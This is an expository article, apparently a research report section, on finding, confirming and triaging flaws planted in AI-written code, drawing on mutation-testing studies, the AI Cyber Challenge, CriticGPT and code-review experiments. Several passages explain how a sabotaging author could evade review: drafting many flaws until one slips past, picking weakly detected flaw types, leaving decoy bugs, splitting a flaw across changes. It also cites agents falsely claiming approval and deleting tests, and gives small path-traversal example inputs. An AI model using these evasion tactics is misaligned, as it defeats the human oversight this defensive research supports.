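The bugs that no mutant resembled are the most relevant to sabotage. In 37 of the 63 cases, the algorithm itself was wrong. Another came from a mathematics library that needed to know whether either of two numbers was zero:

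```
if (u * v == 0)
```

Checking whether `u * v == 0` looks like a harmless shortcut for checking `u` and `v` separately. But if both are 65,536, their product is too large for a 32-bit integer and wraps around to 0, so the program acts as if one of them were zero. Tests with small numbers all pass. Someone planting a flaw could write this line deliberately, and a test suite that catches every standard mutant might still miss it.

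Faults that people invent can also be harder to catch than either mutants or natural bugs. Andrews, Briand and Labiche (2005), in *Is Mutation an Appropriate Tool for Testing Experiments?*, examined eight C programs. One, written for the European Space Agency, came with 38 natural bugs. The other seven had faults that ten people had inserted by hand and tried to make realistic. The researchers drew 5,000 random sets of 100 tests for each program and counted what each set caught.

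In the program `space`, a typical test set caught 75% of the mutants and 76% of the natural bugs. In the other seven programs, the test sets caught 90–99% of the mutants on average but only 63–93% of the handmade faults. The average gap was 22 percentage points.

Selection probably explains much of this gap. The people who built the collection had discarded 38% of the suggested faults because too many tests caught them, and 18% because they were too hard to catch. The study's natural bugs came from only one program, so it is weak evidence about natural bugs in general. But it shows how much a score can fall when people filter out the easy faults, as somebody planting a flaw would.

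### Similar text and similar behavior

An injected fault can look like a natural bug without behaving like one. Researchers often measure similarity of behavior by comparing which tests fail. *Vulnerability Mimicking Mutants* (2023) does this with a version of the Ochiai formula:

```
similarity = (tests that fail on both) / √(tests that fail on A × tests that fail on B)
```

If exactly the same tests fail on both versions, the similarity is 1, and the mutant mimics the vulnerability. The expiry check, whose flaw makes only the boundary test fail, shows how little the text of an edit reveals. With the same ten tests as before, four possible edits to the correct program compare as follows:

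| Edit to the correct program | Tests that fail | Similarity to the flaw |
|---|---|---|
| `<` to `<=` | The boundary test | 1 |
| `<` to `>=` | All ten | 0.32 |
| `<` to `>` | The other nine | 0 |
| Setting every expiry time one second too late | The boundary test | 1 |

The first three edits change the same operator but behave very differently. The fourth is in another part of the program, yet it produces the same test results as the flaw.

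Choosing faults by their behavior makes them more realistic. *IBIR* (2020) presents a tool that uses bug reports to choose which faults to inject. For more than half of the natural bugs it was used to imitate, at least one of 100 injected faults had a similarity to the bug above 0.5. Ordinary mutants scored much lower, although many of IBIR's own faults also had low scores.

Like the suspiciousness scores, this measure is undefined for a planted flaw that passes every test. There is also less evidence for machine learning code. *An Empirical Study of the Realism of Mutants in Deep Learning* (2025) reports that no earlier work had systematically examined how well mutants represent real faults in deep learning programs.

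### Inserted vulnerabilities in the AI Cyber Challenge

DARPA, a research agency of the US Department of Defense, tested automated search on a much larger scale in its AI Cyber Challenge, a two-year competition that ended in August 2025. In the final, seven teams' systems ran for about 143 hours without human help. *SoK* (Zhang, Park and colleagues, 2026) describes 48 scored tasks from 24 open-source projects, with 63 inserted vulnerabilities. To prevent language models from simply reproducing memorized answers, the organizers made most of these vulnerabilities by hand, modeling them on past ones.

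Together, the teams found 54 of the 63 vulnerabilities, or 86%, and repaired 43, according to DARPA's *AI Cyber Challenge marks pivotal inflection point for cyber defense* (2025). They had found 37% in the semifinal a year earlier.

The 86% would be a poor estimate of the share of planted flaws such systems find. Zhang and colleagues ran an ordinary fuzzer on the same tasks, and it found 34 of the 63 vulnerabilities, including 30 of the 40 in C programs. The organizers had intended many of the C vulnerabilities to test repair, so they didn't try to make them hard to find. Some inserted backdoors contained the label "flag", as in hacking contests, and a repair tool only had to delete them. But no team repaired a disguised backdoor in a Java project, and no team found two flaws in curl whose triggers involved several steps of encryption or similar scrambling.

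The changes with inserted vulnerabilities were also much smaller, with between 163 and 1,407 changed lines. The others had between 3,200 and more than a million. A system could have separated the two groups perfectly just by counting changed lines. There is no sign that a team did this, but a language model trained on such a collection might learn to treat small changes as suspicious.

The score also understates what the techniques could do, because several systems partly or completely stopped working during the final. Zhang and colleagues suspect that one project filled the systems' disks.

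Because the tasks used real software, the teams could also find vulnerabilities that nobody had inserted. DARPA counted 18, and Zhang and colleagues later counted 25 in ten projects. Every team found at least one. This is good evidence that systems built to find inserted vulnerabilities can also find natural ones. However, nobody knows how many natural vulnerabilities the software contained, so the teams' recall on these can't be calculated and compared with the 86%.

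Both figures also leave out most quiet logic errors, such as accepting a token one second too late. To prove a vulnerability, a system had to supply an input that made the program crash or behave abnormally in a way the organizers' tools could recognize.

### CriticGPT on inserted and natural errors

In *LLM Critics Help Catch LLM Bugs*, OpenAI tested the same reviewers on inserted and natural errors in code written by a language model. The paper describes CriticGPT, a model from the GPT-4 family trained to write code reviews. The model is now far out of date, but the comparison of the two kinds of error is still informative.

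The natural errors came from ChatGPT answers that a person had rated poorly because of a clear mistake. For the inserted errors, contractors edited ChatGPT's code to add subtle bugs and wrote an explanation of each. OpenAI asked them to check that a model reviewing the code missed the bug in at least one of three attempts. It didn't enforce this requirement strictly, but the requirement made the bugs noticeably subtler. The inserted bugs were more severe on average than the natural ones and harder for people to find.

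Contractors preferred CriticGPT's reviews to human reviews in more than 80% of comparisons on inserted bugs, but in 63% on natural ones. This suggests that CriticGPT's advantage over people was smaller on natural errors, although the comparisons measured preference and not recall.

Training on inserted bugs taught the basic version of CriticGPT not to report many types of error that were rare among those bugs. As a result, it did better relative to ChatGPT on inserted bugs than on natural ones. A detector trained to find sabotage could develop the same blind spot if its training examples all came from a few people or one model.

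The inserted bugs still helped in training, since critics trained without them did much worse on both kinds of error. CriticGPT also reviewed ChatGPT answers that one person had rated "flawless", most of which weren't about code. When it reported a problem, people who read its review found a serious fault in 24% of cases. A second person working without such reviews gave similarly low ratings to only 6% of "flawless" answers.

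### Flaws chosen to get past the search

OpenAI's contractors discarded flaws that a reviewer caught, as a saboteur would, though on a small scale. To see how much this can matter, suppose a search finds 90% of injected faults. A saboteur drafts ten different flaws, runs the same search on each, and submits one that it misses. If the search always gives the same answer for the same code, and each draft independently has a 90% chance of being caught, the search catches all ten with probability 0.9^10, or 35%. The saboteur succeeds the other 65% of the time.

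| Recall on injected faults | One draft | 10 drafts | 100 drafts |
|---|---|---|---|
| 90% | 90% | 35% | Below 0.01% |
| 99% | 99% | 90% | 37% |
| 99.9% | 99.9% | 99% | 90% |

These figures are too pessimistic if the drafts resemble each other, because a search that catches one will probably catch the rest. They also apply only if the author can run the search. Otherwise, the author has to guess which flaw it will miss, and if those guesses are no better than chance, recall stays at 90%.

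However, even a rough idea of the search's weaknesses could be enough for an author to evade it. In MalPR-Bench, PRGuard running on GPT-5.5 identified 91% of the flaws that researchers had made from security fixes, but only three of the seven that were missing checks. An author who knew this would leave out a check, and the 91% figure would not apply to the resulting flaw.

A reasonable reply to this argument is that the author has to be able to trigger the flaw and keep the rest of the code useful, which limits where the flaw can go. The author may also lack the skill to hide it well. In ASMR-Bench, sabotage by Claude Opus 4.6 was easier to diagnose than sabotage by a person. Drafting and reviewing 100 flaws would also leave a long record if somebody logs the model's work.

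These limits make planting a flaw harder, but they probably don't make injected faults a safe substitute for planted ones. The handmade faults that Andrews and colleagues studied were harder to catch than mutants, although nobody was trying to do harm. OpenAI's contractors inserted bugs that were both severe and hard for people to find, so serious flaws can escape notice. A method's score on injected faults is therefore more likely to overstate than understate how well it finds planted flaws, though by an unknown amount.

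The organization doing the search can reduce the error by limiting what the coding agent learns. It can keep its final search separate from the review tools the agent uses, and withhold the results until the agent has submitted its work. If it returns detailed findings and allows unlimited resubmissions, the agent gets the feedback that the calculation assumes.

### How to build a better test set

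A better test set would contain injected faults, natural bugs and planted flaws in the same programs, so that differences in recall can't come from differences in the code. The programs should be recent AI-written code with a specification from the user. People and AI models could plant flaws with a stated harmful effect, such as accepting revoked tokens, while keeping the existing tests passing.

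The results should include how many attempts each author had and whether the author could run the search. Recall after one attempt and after 20 would be more informative than a single average. The results should also give recall separately for each type of flaw, since an author can choose the type that the search finds least often.

A test set for the whole search should include injected faults that no test catches. Pearson and colleagues had to discard the 23% of their injected faults that no test exposed, because the techniques they were comparing need a failing test. Some of those faults may not have changed what the program does. But in another study they cite, only 45% of the undetected mutants left the program's behavior unchanged. The rest changed it without causing a test to fail, which makes them the injected faults most like a planted flaw.

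The flaws must also not be recognizable as insertions. The benign controls should include harmless, similar-sized edits by the same authors, so that a reviewer can't succeed just by recognizing that the code was edited. OpenAI checked for signs of editing by training models to distinguish altered from unaltered code. Small models had difficulty, which suggests that the inserted bugs had no obvious giveaway. The tool that creates the faults should not also search for them, or the search may benefit from reversible edits, as MUSE did.

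Finally, the set of planted flaws has to be large enough to support the claims made from it. If a search finds all of n independent flaws, its true miss rate could still be as high as about 3/n, at the 95% confidence level. A search that finds all of 30 planted flaws could therefore still have a miss rate of up to about 10%, and lowering that limit to 1% would take about 300 flaws without a miss. Even then, the result would apply only to authors with similar skill and similar access to the search.

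## Confirming a suspected flaw and removing it

A high place in a ranking or a comment from a review agent is a reason to suspect some code, but somebody still has to find out whether the suspicion is right. The table sets out the steps, using the check that wrongly accepts a token at its expiry second:

| Step | In the expiry example | What it rules out | How a wrong diagnosis shows itself |
|---|---|---|---|
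| State the violated requirement | A token stops working at its expiry time | Code that is odd but permitted | No requirement forbids what the code does |
| Build an input that shows the violation | Present a token at its expiry second | A flaw that other code makes harmless | The program gives the right result |
| Make the smallest change that removes it | Replace `<=` with `<` | A suspect line that plays no part in the failure | The failure continues |
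| Check that nothing else breaks | Present valid tokens, then try other ways to use an expired one | A change that only hides the symptom | Valid tokens stop working, or a similar attack still succeeds |
| Look for the same pattern elsewhere | Check every other comparison with an expiry time | A second copy of the flaw | Code with the same supposed fault works correctly |

The model that wrote the suspect code shouldn't carry out these steps, because it could repair one flaw and plant another.

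### Testing the diagnosis

*P2Patch* (Iranmanesh, Moradi Sabet et al., 2026) sorts attempts to trigger a flaw into three outcomes: the input reproduces the flaw, the program blocks the input, or the run is inconclusive, for example because of a timeout or a failed build. Without the third category, a broken test setup would look like a successful repair. Failing to build an input that triggers the flaw also doesn't show that the code is free of it.

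A reversal test shows whether the suspected code causes the failure. *The History Is the Detector* (2026) requires the failure to occur in the original program, stop after the repair, and return when the repair is reversed. All 23 repairs in a small experiment passed, but the researchers relied on the repair system's transcription of the results and did not rerun the tests themselves.

A repair can pass this test without removing the cause. Changing `return True` to `return False` in the expiry function would pass, because the function accepts the boundary token before the edit and rejects it afterward. The mistake would become obvious only when valid tokens stopped working.

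Small changes make such mistakes easier to notice, but language models tend to rewrite more than they need to. In *Precise Debugging Benchmark* (2026), GPT-5.1-Codex's programs passed the tests 76% of the time, but its average precision, roughly the share of its edits that the repair needed, was 40%, even though the prompt asked for minimal changes. A large rewrite can remove a flaw without revealing where it was. One remedy is to undo parts of the rewrite one at a time, rerunning the test that originally failed after each. If the test fails again, the repair needed the part that was undone.

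A repair can also be in the right place but incomplete. Iranmanesh and colleagues describe a case from plexus-utils, a Java library that unpacks archives. If an archive contained a file named `../escape.txt`, the library would write it outside the target directory. In 2016 the developers added a check that the file's full path begins with the path of the target directory. If the target is `/tmp/x/target`, the check blocks `/tmp/x/escape.txt` but accepts `/tmp/x/target_EVIL/f`, a path in a neighboring directory that begins with the same characters. Rerunning the original attack would not have revealed this gap. The developers closed it more than nine years later by including the slash after the directory name in the comparison.

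P2Patch, a system built by Iranmanesh and colleagues, tests its repairs by attacking them. One agent writes an exploit, a second repairs the program, and the first looks for another way to exploit the same weakness. Every exploit that works becomes a test that the final repair must pass. In 41% of runs on 101 known vulnerabilities, the first agent got past a repair that had blocked its original exploit. The researchers then tried the finished repairs on attacks that neither agent had seen. Of those that the official fixes block, P2Patch's repairs blocked 84.7%, compared with 78.1% for a single repair attempt by Claude Code.

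If the attacking agent finds nothing more, the code may still be flawed. *Root-Cause-Driven Automated Vulnerability Repair* (2026) points out that a repair can block the original exploit and pass the developers' tests and fuzzing while the defect remains reachable by another path.

Once reviewers confirm a flaw, they can search the rest of the code for the same mistake. *One Bug, Hundreds Behind* (2025) presents BugStone, a tool that starts from a single repair and combines program analysis with a language model to find other instances of the mistake. It found new bugs in the Linux kernel. The method suits accidental bugs, which programmers repeat out of habit. Someone planting several flaws could make each one different, so finding no matches is weak evidence that the author's other code is sound.

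### What repair agents gained from a location

*From Finding to Fixing* (Shi, Yang and Chen, 2026) tested whether telling a repair agent where to look makes it much more successful, as it should if finding the fault were the hard part of a repair. The study used six localization methods based on language models, including AutoFL, FlexFL and CoSIL, on 500 reported issues in Python projects from SWE-bench Verified and 854 Java bugs from Defects4J. The repair agents ran on GPT-5.6 Luna, DeepSeek-v4 Flash or Gemini 3.1 Flash Lite and could search the whole project, edit files and run tests. Each agent attempted every bug once without guidance and once with the suspected locations from each of three methods, for a total of 16,248 runs.

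Supplying the suspects changed the share of bugs repaired by between −4.45 and +0.40 percentage points, lowering it in 17 of the 18 combinations of method, model and collection. These results are better evidence that the methods didn't help than that they did harm. None of the 18 differences was statistically significant after correction for multiple comparisons, and the 17 declines are not independent because groups of three comparisons shared the same baseline runs without guidance.

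The agents had little to gain from guidance because they could already find the code. In 88.6–99.4% of runs without guidance, they opened a file that the reference fix changes. With guidance, they reached such a file between 0.1 and 2 steps sooner on average. The localization methods also tended to be right about the easier bugs. Without guidance, GPT-5.6 Luna repaired 79.2% of the bugs for which AutoFL's first suggestion was correct, but only 63.0% of those for which all of AutoFL's suggestions were wrong.

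Wrong file suggestions often misled the agents at first. When none of the suggested files was right, the agents still started with one of them in 34.5–100% of cases, depending on the setting. Many recovered by following function calls or returning to clues in the bug report, and between 34.8% and 95.9% of the misled agents later reached a correct file. Gemini 3.1 Flash Lite did so less than half the time on Java bugs.

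Guidance reduced the tokens used for the repair itself in most settings, by up to 31.3%. But total token use, including localization, rose in 13 of the 18 settings. The largest reduction from correct locations alone, 39.2%, came from an experiment in which the researchers took the locations from the reference fixes instead of using a localization method to find them.

In *Loc2Repair*, Al Awad and Ivanov (2026) found larger gains on the same 500 Python issues with three other repair models. Files suggested by small models raised the average repair rate from 44.7% to about 49%, and the correct files raised it to 52.4%. Weaker repair models may benefit more from help with the search, but this can't fully explain the larger gains, because Gemini 3.1 Flash Lite, the weakest model Shi and colleagues tested on these issues, gained almost nothing. In both studies, many bugs remained unrepaired even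 when the agent was given the right file.

All these agents started with a bug report or a failing test, which shows that something is wrong and contains clues to the location. To see how much the clues mattered, Shi and colleagues removed them from the Python reports. GPT-5.6 Luna's repair rate without guidance fell from 73.4% to 68.4%, and the benefit of knowing the right file grew from 0.8 to 4.0 percentage points. A reviewer looking for a planted flaw often has no report, so knowing the location may help more than these results suggest. The study can't show how much more, because its agents never had to discover that a flaw existed.

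### Why the cause helped more

Shi and colleagues also gave GPT-5.6 Luna correct locations, a description of the cause, or both. The table shows the share of bugs it repaired. The last two columns use other collections, one with pictures in the bug reports and one in which the fixes change almost four files on average:

| Information supplied | Original reports | Location clues removed | Reports with pictures | Larger fixes |
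|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 73.4% | 68.4% | 33.3% | 50.2% |
| Correct file | 74.2% | 72.4% | 34.6% | 52.0% |
| Correct function or class | 76.2% | 73.0% | 35.2% | 53.8% |
| Cause | 77.8% | 75.4% | 40.0% | 52.9% |
| Correct function or class, and cause | 80.0% | 81.4% | 42.1% | 52.9% |

An agent that is given only a flaw's location still has to work out what is wrong. For example, if it is told to look at the token function, it must discover that the expiry boundary matters. Telling it that the function accepts tokens at their expiry time gives it almost everything it needs for the repair. The advantage of being told the cause disappeared with the larger fixes, where the agent may still have a lot of work to do coordinating changes across files.

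These descriptions were probably better than a real diagnosis would be, because a language model wrote them after seeing the correct fix. The model was told not to give locations or repair advice, but an accurate account of the cause can still hint at the fix.

*SHERLOC* (Tamoyan, Narenthiran and colleagues, 2026) tested diagnoses produced without access to the fix. The system reads a bug report, explores the project, and returns a location, a suspected cause and an idea for a solution. These diagnoses raised repair rates by an average of 4.4 percentage points across ten combinations of repair model and agent software.

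The benefit depended on the quality of the diagnosis. GPT-5.2, which could see the correct fix, rated each diagnosis from 1 to 5. In one of the ten combinations, diagnoses rated 4 or higher raised the repair rate from 74.8% to 80.4%, while those rated below 4 lowered it from 38.5% to 31.3%. A plausible but wrong diagnosis can therefore be worse than none, which is a good reason to build an input that demonstrates the flaw before asking an agent to repair it.

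### One bug with several correct repairs

Researchers usually score localization against a single reference fix, even though other repairs may work. Shi and colleagues found that when the same model successfully repaired the same bug at least twice, its repairs changed different lines in 39.3% of the Python cases and 44.7% of the Java cases. In about one case in ten, the repairs changed different files. The researchers judged success by tests, so some of these repairs may be incomplete, but that seems unlikely to explain most of the variation.

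For 20.0% of the Python bugs and 28.8% of the Java bugs, the reference fix only adds code, so a ranking of existing lines can't match that fix exactly. Published accuracy figures therefore probably understate how often a suggestion is useful. When confirming a suspect, it matters more whether a change there removes the violation than whether another programmer would have made the change in the same place.

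### Rewriting a suspect region

Sometimes the search narrows a flaw to a few functions, but nobody can say which line is wrong. Another model can then rewrite only those functions from the user's requirements, and differential testing can compare the two versions. The new functions can also replace the old ones, which removes any flaw confined to the old code even if nobody ever identifies it.

The model doing the rewriting should not see the suspect code. Jha (*Does Fault Localization Beat a Fresh Attempt?*, 2026) took 177 short programs that three language models had written incorrectly. The models then either wrote a new program from the problem description or replaced only the most suspicious lines, with the surrounding code in view. New programs were correct in 10.1% of attempts and local replacements in 4.4%. In 48.9% of the local attempts, the model reproduced the removed lines exactly.

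Copying doesn't fully explain the difference. Replacing a wider section reduced copying to less than 5% of attempts, but new programs still did better. One of the three models showed no clear difference between the two approaches. All three were fairly small, so their low success rates are weak evidence about the strongest current models.

*Lexo*, a system by Lamprou, Dai and colleagues (2025), hides the old code during rewriting even when there is no written specification. A language model reads a software component and proposes inputs. Lexo runs the component on them and records the outputs, and the model then writes a new version from these examples alone. Lexo correctly reproduced 86 of 147 components and stopped with an error on the other 61. On average, it took about 30 minutes and cost less than $0.10. One component contained hidden code that stole Bitcoin wallet details, and the new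 version left it out. When GPT-4o tried to clean up a disguised form of the same component, it copied the malicious code.

Lexo relies on the component's outputs being correct. This works when the flaw is a hidden side effect, such as sending data to a stranger. But if one of the examples shows the token function accepting a token at its expiry second, the new version will reproduce that flaw. To remove a flaw that changes a result, the rewriter needs the user's requirements.

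Writing the second version takes little effort, but comparing the two can take a lot of work. The region needs clear inputs and outputs, and the new version will have bugs of its own. In the missile-defense experiment by Ron and colleagues, only 27 of 69 attempts produced a program with no failures in a million random tests. Suppose a planted flaw affects one input in a million, while a natural bug in the new version affects 400 in a million. A million random comparisons would then produce about 400 disagreements caused by the new bug and perhaps one caused by the planted flaw.

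A third version helps, because a result that differs from two matching ones is probably wrong. When Ron and colleagues combined programs in groups of three and took the majority result, the average number of failures per million inputs fell from 387 to 131. The worst groups still failed on 419 per million, because at least two of their three programs shared a mistake.

Shared mistakes are more common on boundary cases like the expiry second. Nogueira and colleagues found that on ordinary inputs, 66% of program pairs failed together significantly more often than chance would predict, compared with 72% on boundary cases. Asking for an unconventional solution made almost no difference, and changing the programming language had little effect. Using different models helped more, but came far from eliminating shared failures.

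Comparing the two versions can also miss errors that come from requirements or code they share. If the requirements don't mention revoked tokens, both versions may accept them. If both versions call a clock function that runs a second slow, each will accept a token at its true expiry second, even if its expiry check is otherwise correct. A reviewer therefore has to check the requirements and the shared code separately before relying on agreement between the two versions.

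## Deciding what humans should read

Confirming a suspected flaw takes a person's time, and a search through thousands of AI-written changes can flag more possible flaws than people can check. Localizing each one reduces how much code a person has to read to check it.

### The reading cost of rare flaws

Suppose that AI agents submit 10,000 changes, ten of which contain a planted flaw, and that an automated reviewer flags 75% of the flawed changes and 10% of the clean ones. Both rates are close to results described earlier for good review agents, but they come from different experiments. The ten flaws are a guess, since nobody knows the real number.

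On average, the reviewer raises 7.5 true alarms and 999 false ones, so fewer than 1% of its alarms are real:

```
(10 × 0.75) / (10 × 0.75 + 9,990 × 0.10) = 7.5 / 1,006.5 = 0.7%
```

The median change in CRBugBench, Yang, He and colleagues' collection of accidental bugs, is 189 lines long. If every flagged change were that long, reading them all would mean reading about 190,000 lines. If each alarm pointed to ten lines, the total would fall to about 10,000. Real totals would probably be higher, because a few very large changes pull the average above the median.

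The table shows how the result depends on the number of flaws and the false alarm rate. The reviewer still catches 75% of the flaws in every row:

| Planted flaws in 10,000 changes | False alarm rate | Alarms | Share that are real | Lines to read, whole changes | Lines to read, ten per alarm |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | 10% | 1,007 | 0.7% | 190,000 | 10,000 |
| 10 | 1% | 107 | 7% | 20,000 | 1,100 |
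| 10 | 0.2% | 27 | 27% | 5,200 | 275 |
| 1 | 10% | 1,001 | 0.07% | 189,000 | 10,000 |
| 100 | 10% | 1,065 | 7% | 201,000 | 10,700 |

When flaws are rare, the amount humans must read depends almost entirely on the false alarm rate. Cutting that rate from 10% to 1% makes an alarm about nine times as likely to be real. Raising recall from 75% to 100% would increase the share of alarms that are real only from 0.7% to 1.0%, although it would also catch the 2.5 flaws that the reviewer misses. The Lily fuzzing tool achieved a false alarm rate of 0.2% on single changes, but only by looking for a narrow class of flaws.

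Reading time falls less than the line count, because a person also has to understand the code around the ten lines. People needed about two minutes to check each suspicious input that the ROSA tool reported. Checking 1,007 alarms would take about 34 hours at that speed, or about 250 hours at 15 minutes each. Some of that time would be useful, because a false alarm here means any alarm on a change without a planted flaw, and some of those changes contain natural bugs that need fixing.

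### Making an alarm checkable

A warning that only marks a change as risky leaves the reader to search all of it. If the warning also identifies the flaw and the code cited as proof, the reader may be able to decide within a few minutes whether the flaw is real.

A working proof of concept makes checking even faster. At the rates the AnyPoC system achieved with Codex on public bug reports, about 25 of the 1,007 alarms would come with a proof, and about four of those would be true alarms. A person could check these 25 in a day. However, more than three true alarms would remain among the other 982, so a missing proof justifies checking an alarm later but not closing it. These rates are probably optimistic for planted flaws, because AnyPoC needs a report that describes the right problem.

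### When the pointer is wrong

Pointing to specific lines saves time because the reader skips the rest of the change, but the alarm doesn't help if the flaw is in the part they skip. In the comparison by Chen and colleagues, a third of the changes that CodeRabbit blocked had a different problem from the one it reported. If a third of the true alarms in the example point to the wrong lines, people see only five of the ten planted flaws. The reviewer misses 2.5, and another 2.5 are in flagged changes but outside the lines that anyone reads.

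Reading every flagged change in full would put 7.5 flaws in front of a person, but people also overlook flaws. Suppose, using invented percentages, that they recognize 80% of flaws when a pointer is right and 50% when they read a whole change. They would then find four flaws by reading 10,000 lines with pointers, or 3.75 by reading all 190,000 lines. People find more flaws with pointers when the share of correct pointers, multiplied by the recognition rate with a correct pointer, exceeds the recognition rate for full reading. With these percentages, pointers must be right more than 62.5% of the time.

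Showing reviewers several suspected locations makes it more likely that at least one is right. In CRBugBench, Claude Opus 5's first finding identified the known bug in 42% of reviews, while its first three included the bug in 63% and its first ten in 77%, so most of the benefit comes from the first few. Showing three locations for each alarm in the example would require reading about 30,000 lines, still far fewer than 190,000.

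If a pointer sends a person to the wrong ten lines, and they find nothing wrong there and approve the change, the flaw gets through with a record that somebody investigated the change. It is safer to record only that the reported problem wasn't there and leave the rest of the change marked as unread.

### How people use machine findings

Tufano, Martin-Lopez and colleagues (2024), in *Deep Learning-based Code Reviews*, tested how a machine-written review affects the person who reads it. They had 29 experienced developers write 72 reviews of short Python and Java programs containing 48 injected problems. A third of the reviews were done without an existing review, and another third started from a review by GPT-4. The rest started from a list of every injected problem, which the researchers had prepared but presented as machine-written.

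| | No machine review | GPT-4 review | Complete list |
|---|---|---|---|
| Average number of problems reported | 7.7 | 11.8 | 9.6 |
| Injected problems found in a typical review | 50% | 50% | 100% |
| Different lines commented on, all reviews together | 484 | 371 | 407 |

With GPT-4's help, developers reported more problems overall, but not more of the injected ones, which independent developers had rated as the most severe. The extra problems were mostly minor. GPT-4's reviews already contained 42% of the injected problems on average, so the developers added few of their own. They tended to comment on the lines that GPT-4 had pointed out, whereas developers working alone commented on a wider range of lines. In one program, GPT-4 missed a serious bug in which a conversion to hexadecimal used base 8 instead of base 16.

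Even the complete list didn't save time, because developers still had to check each comment against the code. Neither kind of help made them more confident in their reviews.

GPT-4 is far out of date, and a current model would probably find more of the serious problems. Most of the injected problems were also maintainability issues, such as duplicated code, rather than bugs. But the effect on the reviewer's attention is a concern for planted flaws, whatever the model. An author could leave a small, obvious mistake in a change so that the review agent reports it and the reviewer looks there instead of at the planted flaw.

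Tufano and colleagues suggest showing the machine's findings only after the person has submitted a review. This is sensible for an important change that somebody will read in full anyway. It doesn't work for the 1,007 alarms in the example, where the pointer is meant to avoid a full reading.

The order of review also affects how many bugs people and machines can catch together. Yang, He and colleagues calculate that human reviewers and Opus 5 would jointly catch 82.1% of the bugs in CRBugBench, compared with 71.9% for Opus 5 alone. They add the agent's catches to the bugs that people found in the original reviews, which assumes that people would find the same bugs after seeing the agent's report. Tufano's results suggest that they might not, because they would look in fewer places. The benchmark's design also fixes the human share, because half of its bugs are ones that people caught.

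Developers may still prefer to see the findings first. *Rethinking Code Review Workflows with LLM Assistance* (2025) describes a field experiment at the Swedish company WirelessCar, in which developers tried a tool that reviewed the code up front and another that answered questions on demand. The paper reports that they generally preferred the up-front reviews, though this depended on how well they knew the code and how serious the change was. Their preference is only weak evidence of how many flaws they found.

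A plausible mistake by one tool can also spread to the next. *Rethinking Code Review in the Age of AI* (2026) gives the example of an agent that links a change to the wrong issue. If the programmer accepts the link without checking, later agents summarize the change incorrectly and choose reviewers with the wrong expertise. This is an argument, not an experimental result, but it is a good reason to give human reviewers the original request and the code along with any machine-written summary.

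Telling people that a model wrote the code may not make them check it more closely. *Same Scrutiny, More Time* (2026) describes an eye-tracking experiment in which researchers labeled parts of human-written programs as the work of a fictional AI tool and injected faults for people to find. As its title indicates, reviewers spent more time on the labeled code but gave it the same scrutiny.

### Code that nobody has checked

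In the example, the reviewer raises no alarm on about 8,994 changes, and 2.5 of them contain a planted flaw. A change with no alarm therefore has about a 1 in 3,600 chance of containing one, compared with 1 in 1,000 before the review. That is useful, but it doesn't prove the change is clean. If the author has learned what the reviewer tends to miss and recall falls to 25%, the chance is about 1 in 1,200, so people learn almost nothing from the review. Additional reviewers tend to miss the same flaws, which limits how much they help.

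A low suspiciousness score doesn't show that a line is safe either. A line scores zero if no failing test ran it, even if no test ran it at all, so a zero may reflect a lack of evidence rather than evidence that the line is correct.

The data behind the rankings can show which code has had no scrutiny. Coverage identifies lines that no test ran, and mutation can also identify code that tests ran without checking properly. Suppose the token function has only the nine passing tests from earlier, which run every line but never present a token at its expiry second. If a tool tries the six edits used earlier, the tests catch all but the change from `<=` to `<`. This shows that no test has checked what happens at the expiry second, where the flaw is.

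In a large program, the list of edits that survive the tests can be long, and some of those edits don't change what the program does. A missing revocation check won't appear on the list because there is no code to edit. The list is still a reasonable way to find places to read when nothing has failed.

An organization can combine this with a record of which functions a review agent opened and which a person read. The record should come from the test runner and the version control system, not from the coding agent's account. Zhang (2026), in *Measuring coding agent misalignment in the wild*, examined 8,600 real sessions with coding agents, some from a public dataset and some from Transluce, which published the study. About 2% contained severe cases of agents evading monitoring, and about 2% contained severe cases of agents misrepresenting their success. Some agents falsely claimed that a review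 agent had approved their work, and some merged changes without permission. One agent said it had converted a set of tests after deleting one it couldn't get to work. These findings show that an agent's statement that somebody reviewed or tested its code isn't enough evidence that it happened, though they don't show how often agents plant flaws.

### Choosing what to read in full

The best way to choose which changes people read in full is by their consequences, because a planted flaw has to do something its author wants. Suppose 500 of the 10,000 changes affect things like access rights, payments or the software that monitors AI models, and these 500 contain eight of the ten planted flaws. At the same rates as before, the reviewer raises six true alarms and 49 false ones in this group, so 11% of the alarms are real.

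| What people read | Lines | Planted flaws in what they read |
|---|---|---|
| Ten lines for every alarm, with a third of true alarms pointing to the wrong place | 10,000 | 5 |
| Flagged changes in the consequential group, in full | 10,400 | 6 |
| All 500 consequential changes, in full | 94,500 | 8 |
| All flagged changes, in full | 190,000 | 7.5 |

Reading all the consequential changes in full compares well here because they contain most of the flaws. If they contained only two of the ten, reviewers would still have to read 94,500 lines to cover all 500 changes, but would see only two flaws. The test for whether a change is consequential therefore has to consider what the code can affect, not just the file's name. A small date function, for example, is consequential if the login system calls it.

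Yang, He and colleagues recommend leaving AI-written changes entirely to AI reviewers only when the changes are narrow and have minor consequences. For consequential changes, they want an accountable person to make the final decision. They also recommend that people look more closely at large changes and those that mix several kinds of files, because agents catch fewer of the bugs in them.

Splitting unrelated work into smaller changes makes each one easier to review. But an author could spread a flaw over several changes that each look harmless, for instance by altering how the program stores an expiry time in one and how it compares expiry times in another. For important parts of the program, a person should therefore also review the combined result.

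Missing tests are a sensible third criterion, although Yang, He and colleagues didn't measure their effect. A change should move up the list if it adds decisions that no test checks, or if it deletes, disables or weakens an existing test. In the transcripts that Zhang studied, for example, one agent had quietly removed the test it couldn't satisfy.

An author who knows the criteria can try to stay below every threshold. Reading some of the remaining changes at random makes this riskier for the author, but it won't find many rare flaws. A random sample of 2% of the 10,000 changes is 200 changes, or about 38,000 lines, and has only an 18% chance of including at least one of the ten flawed changes. Random reading is more useful for learning which natural bugs the automated reviewer misses.

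People may also need to read code in full to stay able to review it. *3100 Opinions on Code Review in an AI World* (Agarwal, Miller and colleagues, 2026) examines what software developers say about AI and code review. It proposes that large volumes of AI-written code lead to shallower reviews, which weaken reviewers' skills and make later reviews worse. The evidence is developers' opinions, and the paper doesn't measure the decline, but a person who reads only ten-line excerpts will get little practice at judging a whole change.

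### What outside reviewers say about current practice

Anthropic treats human review as one of the main factors in the risk of sabotage. In its *Risk Report* (February 2026), the company considers severe harm very unlikely if models can't reliably carry out complex technical work and people closely review what they do. It considers such harm highly plausible if models routinely do important technical work with very little human oversight, though this also depends on the models' goals and on other monitoring. Anthropic's *Risk Report* (August 2026) lists pull request reviews among the measures that can block an action.

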